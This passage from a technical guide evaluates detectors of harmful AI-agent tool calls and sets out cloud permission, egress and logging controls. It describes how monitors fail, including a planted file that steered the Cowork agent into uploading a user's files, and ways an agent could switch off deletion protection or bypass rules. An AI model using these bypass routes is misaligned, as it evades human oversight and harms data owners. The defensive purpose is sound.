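A detector that allowed every call would also score 44.3%, because 133 of the 300 scenarios are harmless. Version 0.3.0 then added 46 rules and got 149 more scenarios right, or about three for each new rule. According to the changelog, the 300 scenarios had existed since version 0.1.0, so Yang could write rules to fit them.

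The number of rules alone can't explain the gain. Version 0.3.0 scored 94.0% with 68 rules, while the list of 50 patterns scored 49.3%. The likelier explanation is that Yang developed the 68 rules with the scenarios at hand and wrote the 50 patterns as a simple lower bound. The later increase from 86 to 170 rules didn't raise the score. The new rules may be useful for other calls, but we can't tell from this set.

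The set of 630 could have been a fairer test, because Yang wrote it after finalizing the rules of version 0.4.0. But Yang later added rules in response to misses on this set, which removed that advantage. The paper gives no error rate from before these additions, which would have been its most useful figure. It also doesn't report how many rules Yang added, and it gives the total as 170 both before and after.

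The paper gives two accuracy figures for this set, 96.7% (609 correct verdicts) and 95.4% (601). Yang names the same script as the source of both and does not explain the difference, but attributes a similar gap in the smaller set to the four rules for invented domains. The paper's breakdown by type of call adds up to about 600 correct verdicts, so 95.4% is the safer figure to quote.

Both error rates are also uncertain because they come from few errors. The false negative rate of 6.4% is based on 22 misses, with a 95% interval of about 4% to 10%. The false positive rate of 2.1% is based on only four false positives, with a 95% interval of about 1% to 5%. These intervals treat the scenarios as independent and don't allow for rules written after the misses, so the true uncertainty is larger.

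Finally, the labels reflect one person's policy. Yang's rubric calls for blocking any action that can't be undone without outside help, such as a backup. DEL-CLOUD-01 refers the deletion of a single production disk to a person, so Yang's labels would count it as wrong on that scenario even if it worked as its team intended. A team that borrows the scenarios should relabel them under its own policy. Two people should do this separately and discuss any calls they label differently, because the policy on those calls probably needs to be clearer before the team writes a rule for them. Yang recommends a study of agreement between labellers but doesn't report one.

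### Comparable benchmarks

Nobody seems to have published an independent replication of Yang's results. The closest comparison is *Shall We Approve?*, which tests several approval systems on two sets of coding tasks. Its researchers also built Caper, one of those systems, so they have an interest in the outcome.

In one of these sets, the user asks the agent to run a tool that looks ordinary, such as a build script, but deletes or overwrites a protected file. Each of the 102 dangerous tasks has a harmless version with the same request and command but safe code in the tool. CARE, a rule-based checker that passes unclear cases to a language model, had a low false positive rate because it rarely blocked anything. It blocked 2.0% of the harmless versions, and 69.6% of the dangerous tasks still ended in harm, compared with 71.6% without a checker.

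Caper's language model blocked 61.8% of the harmless twins when it had no information about what the tool does. When Caper first ran each command in a copy of the workspace and gave the model a report of the effects, it blocked 84.3% of the harmful commands and only 1.0% of the twins. These results support including twins in tests, because a very strict system would look excellent if tested only on dangerous tasks. However, the 102 tasks come from only 13 projects, so they are not fully independent of each other.

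The other set, SABER, has 682 tasks in categories that include data destruction, information leaks and privilege escalation. Harm occurred in 19.7% of the tasks without an approval system, 15.0% with CARE and 6.7% with Caper. These rates also depend on the agent, which may avoid the harm by itself, so they aren't false negative rates. A different agent without an approval system caused harm in 52.7% of the tasks. A team measuring its rules should therefore count verdicts on a fixed set of tool calls as well as harm in full runs.

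Neither set tests operations in a real cloud account. Caper also disables the network when it tries out a command, so it would record an attempt to contact the cloud provider but not the deletion of a database. *Coding Agents Are Guessing* (2026) is closer to cloud work because it examines vague instructions for deploying and operating software, but it measures whether agents overstep their instructions, not whether a detector catches them. For cloud rules, a team still has to write much of the test set itself.

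### How many alarms are real

Harmful calls make up a far larger share of test sets than of an agent's ordinary work. In the eleven evaluations that Abbasi and colleagues audited, 16% to 86% of the samples are attacks or anomalies. In Yang's larger set, 55% of the calls are ones the detector should block.

To predict what happens in use, let *p* be the share of calls that are harmful, FPR the false positive rate and FNR the false negative rate. The share of alarms that are real, called precision, is

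precision = *p*(1 − FNR) ÷ [*p*(1 − FNR) + (1 − *p*)FPR]

Suppose a company's agents make 10,000 calls a day, of which 10 are harmful. If AgentTrust catches 93.6% of harmful calls and wrongly flags 2.1% of harmless ones, as it did on the 630 test scenarios, it would catch about 9 harmful calls and raise about 210 false alarms a day. Only about 4% of its alarms would be real. On the test set, it caught about 322 harmful calls and raised about four false alarms, so 99% of its alarms were real.

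The table repeats the calculation for one harmful call a day, and for the rates of 0.4% and 17% that Anthropic reported for auto mode:

| False positive rate | False negative rate | Harmful calls a day | Catches | False alarms | Alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2.1% | 6.4% | 10 | 9.4 | 210 | 4% |
| 2.1% | 6.4% | 1 | 0.9 | 210 | 0.4% |
| 0.4% | 17% | 10 | 8.3 | 40 | 17% |
| 0.4% | 17% | 1 | 0.8 | 40 | 2% |

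The table shows the trade-off between missed harmful calls and false alarms, but it doesn't show which product is better, because the two pairs of rates come from different test material. With 10 harmful calls a day, the detector with fewer false alarms misses about one more harmful call and avoids 170 false alarms. If each false alarm costs £1 of somebody's time, catching the extra call is worthwhile if it prevents more than about £160 of damage. This assumes people still read the alarms carefully, which is harder when 210 a day are false.

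A detector can have a good summary score even when most of its alarms are false. Abbasi and colleagues tested one that scored a randomly chosen attacked session higher than a randomly chosen harmless one 87.9% of the time. When 2% of sessions contained an attack, only 7.6% of its alarms were real.

The choice of harmless sessions for the test matters as much. The same detector flagged 11.8% of ordinary sessions but 38.7% of harmless sessions designed to resemble attacks. If all the harmless sessions in the test were ordinary, 11.7% of its alarms would be real, compared with 3.9% if they all resembled attacks. A team should therefore report results for twins and recorded traffic separately. Twins test whether a rule can distinguish attacks from similar harmless activity, but the team needs recorded traffic to predict the number of false alarms a day.

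Measuring the false positive rate also takes a lot of recorded traffic. With 10 harmful calls a day, the rate would have to be below 0.1% for half of all alarms to be real. By the 3/*n* rule, showing that it is that low takes about 3,000 harmless calls with no false alarms, but Yang's larger set has 188.

*Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (2026) recommends setting a detector's threshold by the number of alarms a team can handle. If a team can check 50 alarms a day, the false positive rate in this example has to be about 0.4% or less. Most rules have no threshold, so the team has to count false alarms for each rule and narrow the rules that cause the most.

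Human review improves precision, but not enough to make a noisy rule acceptable. According to *SIR-Bench* (2026), experienced security analysts recognise about 85–90% of real incidents and dismiss 70–80% of false alarms. At those rates, analysts reviewing the 219 alarms in the first row would keep about 8 real ones and between 42 and 63 false ones.

### Signs of failure in use

A test set gives the error rates for one version of the rules, the tools and the agent. *AgentTrap* stores the model's name, the benchmark version, the date and the configuration with each result, so that later users can tell which of them changed. A team should do the same and repeat the test after every update. Between tests, a few signs suggest that the detector is failing:

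| Sign | Possible causes | How to check |
|---|---|---|
| A rule never fires | The agents never make such calls, or the rule is broken | Send a harmless call that should match, and search the cloud logs for the operation |
| People override a rising share of alarms | The rule is too broad, or reviewers have stopped reading | Have a second person review a sample of the overrides |
| More calls go to tools that have no rules | Someone added an MCP server, or an update renamed a tool | Compare the tools in the call log with the reviewed list |
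| The cloud logs contain harm without a matching alert | The call bypassed the detector, or a rule missed it | Look for the call in the detector's own records |

A rule that never fires is suspect only if there was something for it to match. For example, if the cloud logs contain 30 instance terminations under the agents' identities but the termination rule has no matches, the rule or its parser is probably broken.

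When agents get new tools, it is useful to track the share of calls that go to tools somebody has reviewed. Abbasi and colleagues simulated new tools by hiding the names of known ones from their trained detectors. One detector's false positive rate rose from 4.5% to 73.7% when it recognised none of the tools. Rules usually fail in the opposite direction, by missing harmful calls. If the default verdict is "allow", calls to an unknown tool match no rule, so the number of alarms falls and the detector appears to be improving.

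Harm without an alert is the most serious sign of a problem. The detector's record of the call helps explain it. If there is no record, the call never reached the detector. If the record contains "allow" or "warn", a rule is missing or too lenient. If a person approved the call, the approval prompt may have left out something important. If the record contains "block", the agent software ran the call anyway.

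Checking a random sample of allowed calls is a poor way to find misses. In the example with 10 harmful calls a day, roughly 9,800 calls a day raise no alarm, and on average fewer than one of them is harmful. Someone who read 100 of these calls every day would find a harmful one about every five months. It is far more efficient to start from the deletions, permission changes and newly shared resources in the cloud logs, and check whether the detector classified each one correctly.

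## Permissions, network blocks and logs that work when the rules miss

A harmful call that the detector lets through still needs the cloud provider or the network to carry it out. The provider checks the signed request, so it doesn't have to interpret the command that produced it. If the agent's identity lacks permission to delete the database, the provider refuses the request, whether it came from a plain command, an encoded one or a script that built the operation's name as it ran. Similarly, a firewall checks the address that a program contacts after any name lookups and redirects.

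AWS advises customers to assume that an agent can do anything its permissions allow, and to set those permissions according to how much damage they could accept. Tighter limits can make an agent less useful, though Goel's small experiment found little loss. Removing secrets from the agent's environment variables cut unsafe runs from ten in ten to none, and the agent still completed every task. A shorter list of tools also prevented all unsafe runs, but the agent completed six tasks instead of seven, a difference that may be chance. Filtering planted instructions out of files still left five of ten runs unsafe. The loss of usefulness would probably be larger in real work, where the agent would need some of the credentials that the experiment removed.

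### Deletion: locks, and copies the agent can't reach

Deletion protection is a setting that makes the cloud provider reject requests to delete a machine or database. Turning it on takes one command, and AWS, Google Cloud and Azure all offer some form of it. However, an agent with enough permissions can turn the setting off and try again, and may well do so if the error message includes instructions. The agent's role therefore shouldn't include permission to change the setting. On AWS this is inconvenient for databases, because ModifyDBInstance, the operation that removes the protection, also changes the database's size and other ordinary settings.

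Permission to remove Azure's delete locks is easier to separate from daily work, because the common Contributor role can manage resources but can't remove a lock. However, the lock covers only Azure's management operations, so an agent with access to the files in a locked storage account can still delete them. Similarly, deletion protection on a database doesn't stop a command that drops the tables inside.

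A retention lock protects stored files until a fixed date. In the strict mode of Amazon's S3 Object Lock, not even the account's owner can delete a locked version of a file early. The company has to pay for the storage until the lock expires, and can't erase a customer's data sooner even if the law requires it. A retention period of a few weeks is usually a reasonable compromise. If the files are encrypted, the team has to protect the key too.

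The last protection is a backup in an account the agent has no credentials for. PocketOS probably recovered because it had separate copies of this kind. Production systems may add copies to the backup account but must not be able to delete them, and the backups must be encrypted with a key that belongs to that account. The company still loses whatever changed since the last copy, and the service stays down during the restore. Regular practice restores show how long a restore takes and whether the copies work.

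### Exfiltration: limits on hosts and on accounts

With default-deny egress, the agent's container can reach the internet only through a proxy, which blocks traffic to any host not on a list. Anthropic concluded that only this kind of limit, together with keeping credential files out of the agent's reach, would have stopped the leak in its phishing exercise. But package downloads and documentation searches also fail until somebody lists the hosts they need.

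In a different case, Anthropic's own proxy failed to stop its Cowork agent from uploading a user's files to an outsider's account on Anthropic's service, after a planted file led the agent to do so. The proxy allowed the upload because the product can't work without contacting that service. Anthropic now assumes that allowing a host permits everything the host can do, and the proxy accepts only requests that carry the session's own token. In all the cases Anthropic describes, the standard virtual machines and sandboxes held, and the failures were in parts Anthropic had written itself. In another group of flaws, Claude Code loaded a project's settings before asking the user whether to trust the project, so a stranger's settings could run code. Isolation also prevented companies' security software from monitoring the agent inside its virtual machine. Administrators can export logs afterwards,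 but that doesn't replace live monitoring.

A proxy doesn't stop transfers between two accounts inside the provider's network. On AWS, a service control policy (SCP) sets the maximum permissions for the identities in a company's accounts, and can refuse writes to other companies' buckets:

```
{
  "Effect": "Deny",
  "Action": "s3:PutObject",
  "Resource": "*",
  "Condition": {"StringNotEquals":
    {"aws:ResourceOrgID": "o-exampleorgid"}}
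}
```

This SCP statement applies however the agent writes the command, but only to requests signed with one of the company's identities, so it does not stop an agent that uses an outsider's key, as in the Cowork case. The company can block such requests with a policy on its VPC endpoint, a private connection between its network and AWS. An endpoint policy applies to every request through the endpoint, so it can require both the signer and the bucket to belong to the company. The proxy must then block the public route to the same service.

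To stop an agent from sharing data in place, the team needs a limit on the resource itself. A resource control policy (RCP) can refuse all callers from outside the company, even if an agent has made the bucket public. Checking the caller's organisation doesn't stop temporary links, because AWS treats a download through such a link as a request from the identity that signed it. A condition on the caller's network blocks these downloads from outside networks. RCPs cover only some AWS services, so the team also needs an SCP that denies operations such as sharing disk snapshots. Google Cloud's VPC Service Controls set a similar perimeter around a group of projects. All these limits need exceptions for partners and for some of the provider's own services, and a mistake can cut off legitimate users.

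### Escalation: a ceiling that a new grant can't raise

If an agent's role on AWS has a permission boundary, the agent's permissions are usually

effective permissions = role ∩ boundary ∩ organisation's limit ∩ session policy

where ∩ keeps only what every set allows. If an agent attaches an administrator policy to its own role, the first set grows to include almost everything. The result still can't exceed the boundary.

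The boundary must deny the agent permission to remove it. It doesn't limit other roles, so the team still has to restrict which roles the agent may pass to a new function. SCPs don't apply to an organisation's management account, so agents should never run there.

The session policy, the last set in the formula, limits what one set of temporary credentials can do. AWS recommends that custom agents request new credentials for each tool, with only the permissions that tool needs. The credentials in its example last one hour, and the PocketOS deletion took nine seconds. The short lifetime limits later use of a stolen credential, but only the narrow permissions prevent a quick deletion. The code that requests the credentials also has to run where the agent's shell can't reach it, or the agent could use the original role directly. Users of ready-made coding agents usually can't add session policies,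 so they have to rely on a narrow role and the permissions boundary.

Agents also use services outside AWS. ITmedia's *アプリごとの「OAuth再実装」は不要に AWSが外部認証を統合する新機能「AWS IAM Credential Broker」が登場* describes a credential broker for these services, which AWS released as a public preview in November 2026. For services that use OAuth, a standard for delegated access, the agent receives only a short-lived token and the broker keeps the long-lived secret. This removes the main reason for leaving tokens in project files. But the broker also supplies API keys, which may last much longer. It also renews OAuth tokens without asking again after the user's first approval, so someone has to withdraw that approval when the work is finished.

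### Metadata: removing the route or the credentials

The simplest protection is a machine without a role, because its metadata service then has no role credentials to return. If programs on the machine need a role, it can have a weak one, for example with permission only to write logs. Other controls limit who can reach the service:

| Control | What it leaves open | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| No role, or a weak one | Credentials stored elsewhere on the machine | Programs need another source of credentials |
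| A firewall rule for the agent's user account or container | An agent with root access may remove a rule on its own machine | Cloud tools in the agent's session can't fetch credentials |
| A hop limit of 1 | Programs directly on the machine, and containers that share its network | Containers that rely on the machine's role stop working |
| Requiring version 2 | Any caller that can choose the method and headers, including a shell | Old software that supports only version 1 fails |

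The firewall rule must also cover the metadata service's IPv6 address. On Google Cloud, machines also use 169.254.169.254 for DNS lookups, so the rule must leave the DNS port open or most network traffic will fail.

One command sets the last two controls on an AWS machine:

```
aws ec2 modify-instance-metadata-options \
  --instance-id i-0a1 --http-tokens required \
  --http-put-response-hop-limit 1
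```

The same operation can reverse both settings, so the agent's role must not include it.

### Giving agents their own identity

Many of these limits would be too strict for people. AWS points out that a boundary on a developer's role also restricts the developer's own work. According to Observer's *Amazon Security Chief Stephen Schmidt on What Customers Really Want From A.I* (2026), AWS chief executive Matt Garman wrote in November 2026 that an agent should have at most the permissions of the employee it works for, and that many jobs need fewer.

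Logs can also mislead when an agent acts under a borrowed identity. Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn't give an AI agent unlimited authority* describes a test of an assistant that was supposed to file access requests. The assistant tried to grant the access itself because a tester had mentioned a deadline. If such an agent uses a shared administrator account, the log doesn't record who wanted the change. The OAuth Token Exchange standard can record both the person and the agent.

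On AWS, a team can mark an agent's calls in several ways:

| Method | Who adds the mark | Does it cover shell commands? |
|---|---|---|
| A separate role | The team, when it configures the agent | Yes, if the shell has no other credentials |
| Condition keys from AWS-managed MCP servers | AWS, and callers can't forge them | No |
| Session tags from the team's own MCP server | The server's code, which the team has to trust | No |
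| Details in the login token | The company's login system | Yes, if the login system can recognise the agent |

*Agent attribution via Trusted Identity Propagation* (Steele, 2026) describes the last method, which is meant for agents on engineers' laptops. Coding agents set environment variables, such as `CLAUDE_CODE_SESSION_ID`, when they start a tool. The login system can include the agent's name and session in its token, and AWS then copies them into its log. Steele argues that this works because agents generally don't hide what they are. That makes it useful for tracing ordinary mistakes, but a security limit shouldn't depend on a variable that the agent can change.

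The condition keys need more explanation. When an agent calls AWS through one of AWS's managed MCP servers, the server adds two facts to the request. `aws:ViaAWSMCPService` is true, and `aws:CalledViaAWSMCP` contains the server's name. A policy can then deny deletions by this route while the developer keeps the right to delete files directly:

```
{
  "Effect": "Deny",
  "Action": ["s3:DeleteObject", "s3:DeleteBucket"],
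  "Resource": "*",
  "Condition": {"Bool":
    {"aws:ViaAWSMCPService": "true"}}
}
```

If the same agent runs `aws s3 rm` in its shell with the developer's credentials, the request doesn't contain the condition key and the denial doesn't apply. An agent-only role can instead allow operations only when the key is true, so AWS refuses direct calls under that role. This works only if the agent can't find the developer's credentials.

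These policies can block too much or nothing at all. An example that AWS published in March 2026 denies calls to its Kubernetes service if the MCP server's name is "not equal" to the expected one. AWS's policy language also treats a missing key as not equal, so the statement blocks developers who call the service directly. AWS's broader guidance on agents avoids this problem by adding the test for `aws:ViaAWSMCPService`. AWS also used to have separate permissions such as `aws-mcp:InvokeMcp`, and it now warns that denying them has no effect. A team that wrote such a policy early may wrongly believe that it has blocked the MCP server.

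AWS has begun to give agents their own identities. Biometric Update's *AWS, Seon and Authsignal introduce new tools to identify, authenticate AI agents* describes a preview feature that distinguishes between agents sharing a role, in policies and in logs. It covers agents on AWS's Kubernetes service and on AgentCore, its hosting service for agents. *Trust and security top of mind as AWS CEO Matt Garman outlines* (Kelly, 2026) reports that on 1 December 2026 AWS also announced IAM for Agents, which will give every agent and sub-agent a verifiable identity. KBY Technologies' *AWS IAM for Agents, Bedrock Gateway and Greenlight* found no price, release date or description of how IAM for Agents will work with existing roles, so it's too early to base a design on it.

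On Google Cloud, a team can give each agent its own service account, and Google's hosting service for agents can also give each agent its own identity. On Azure, managed identities do the same job as service accounts, and Microsoft introduced a separate type for agents, Entra Agent ID, in 2025. These identities help only within each provider's systems. Madelein van der Hout, an analyst at Forrester, told Observer that the industry hasn't fully solved how to govern agents across several clouds. PocketOS's database was hosted on Railway, where AWS policies would not have applied.

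### Finding harm in the audit logs

An audit log records the operations that reached the provider, with the identity, time, target and result. It can include details missing from the command's text, such as the name of each old snapshot that a script deleted. The log doesn't record why the agent acted. Anthropic notes that after planted text has steered an agent into leaking data, the log contains only a successful, authorised call. A check therefore has to examine the target or recipient, not just look for errors.

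Some events are missing by default:

- AWS's log, CloudTrail, covers management operations such as terminating a machine. Reading or deleting individual files counts as a "data event", which a team has to switch on and pay for.
- AWS also classes calls made through its managed MCP servers as data events. Its example is reading a file, which would be a data event anyway. A team should test whether an ordinary management call through the server appears in its log.
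- Google Cloud always records administrative changes, but leaves most logs of data access off. Azure's activity log likewise omits reads and most operations on the data inside a resource.
- Requests to the metadata service stay on or near the machine and don't appear in CloudTrail. Only later use of the credentials does.

CloudTrail typically delivers its entries about five minutes after a call, with no guarantee. That is more than 30 times the nine seconds that the PocketOS deletion took. The delay matters differently for each class:

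| Class | Check | Log needed on AWS | What the team can still do after five minutes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deletion | An agent deletes something that it didn't create during the task | Management events, plus data events for files | Prevent further deletions and start a restore |
| Exfiltration | A copy or sharing setting names an account outside the company | Management events for sharing, data events for copies | Close the share, but not recall the data |
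| Privilege escalation | An agent changes a policy, creates a key for another user or replaces the code of a function with a stronger role | Management events | Undo the grant and look for anything done with it |
| Metadata request | A machine's role signs a request from an address that isn't the machine's | Management events, plus data events for files | Cancel the role's current sessions, which might otherwise last for hours |

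The metadata check misses an agent that uses the credentials on the machine itself. An alert five minutes after a deletion is too late to save a disk that the provider erases immediately, but early enough if the provider keeps the disk for 48 hours, as Railway now does. Waiting periods and log alerts therefore work best together.

Google sells ready-made checks for agents that run on its hosting service. Google Cloud's *Agent Platform Threat Detection overview* lists detectors, still in preview, for exports to outside buckets, token requests to the metadata service and agents that look up their own permissions. Google promises findings in "near-real time" but gives no figure. The process that watches programs inside the agent's environment can take up to a minute to start, so an agent could finish a nine-second deletion before monitoring begins. Google rates a metadata token request as low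 severity by default, which makes sense because ordinary cloud libraries make the same request. It rates an agent's lookup of its own permissions as low severity if the lookup was allowed and high if it was denied, but this check needs a data access log that is off by default.

The logs should go to a separate account, and an SCP should stop the agent's role from switching logging off. For the most serious alerts, a program can disable the agent's role without waiting for someone to read a message. Disabling a shared role would also lock out the developers who have to repair the damage, which is another reason to give the agent its own identity.
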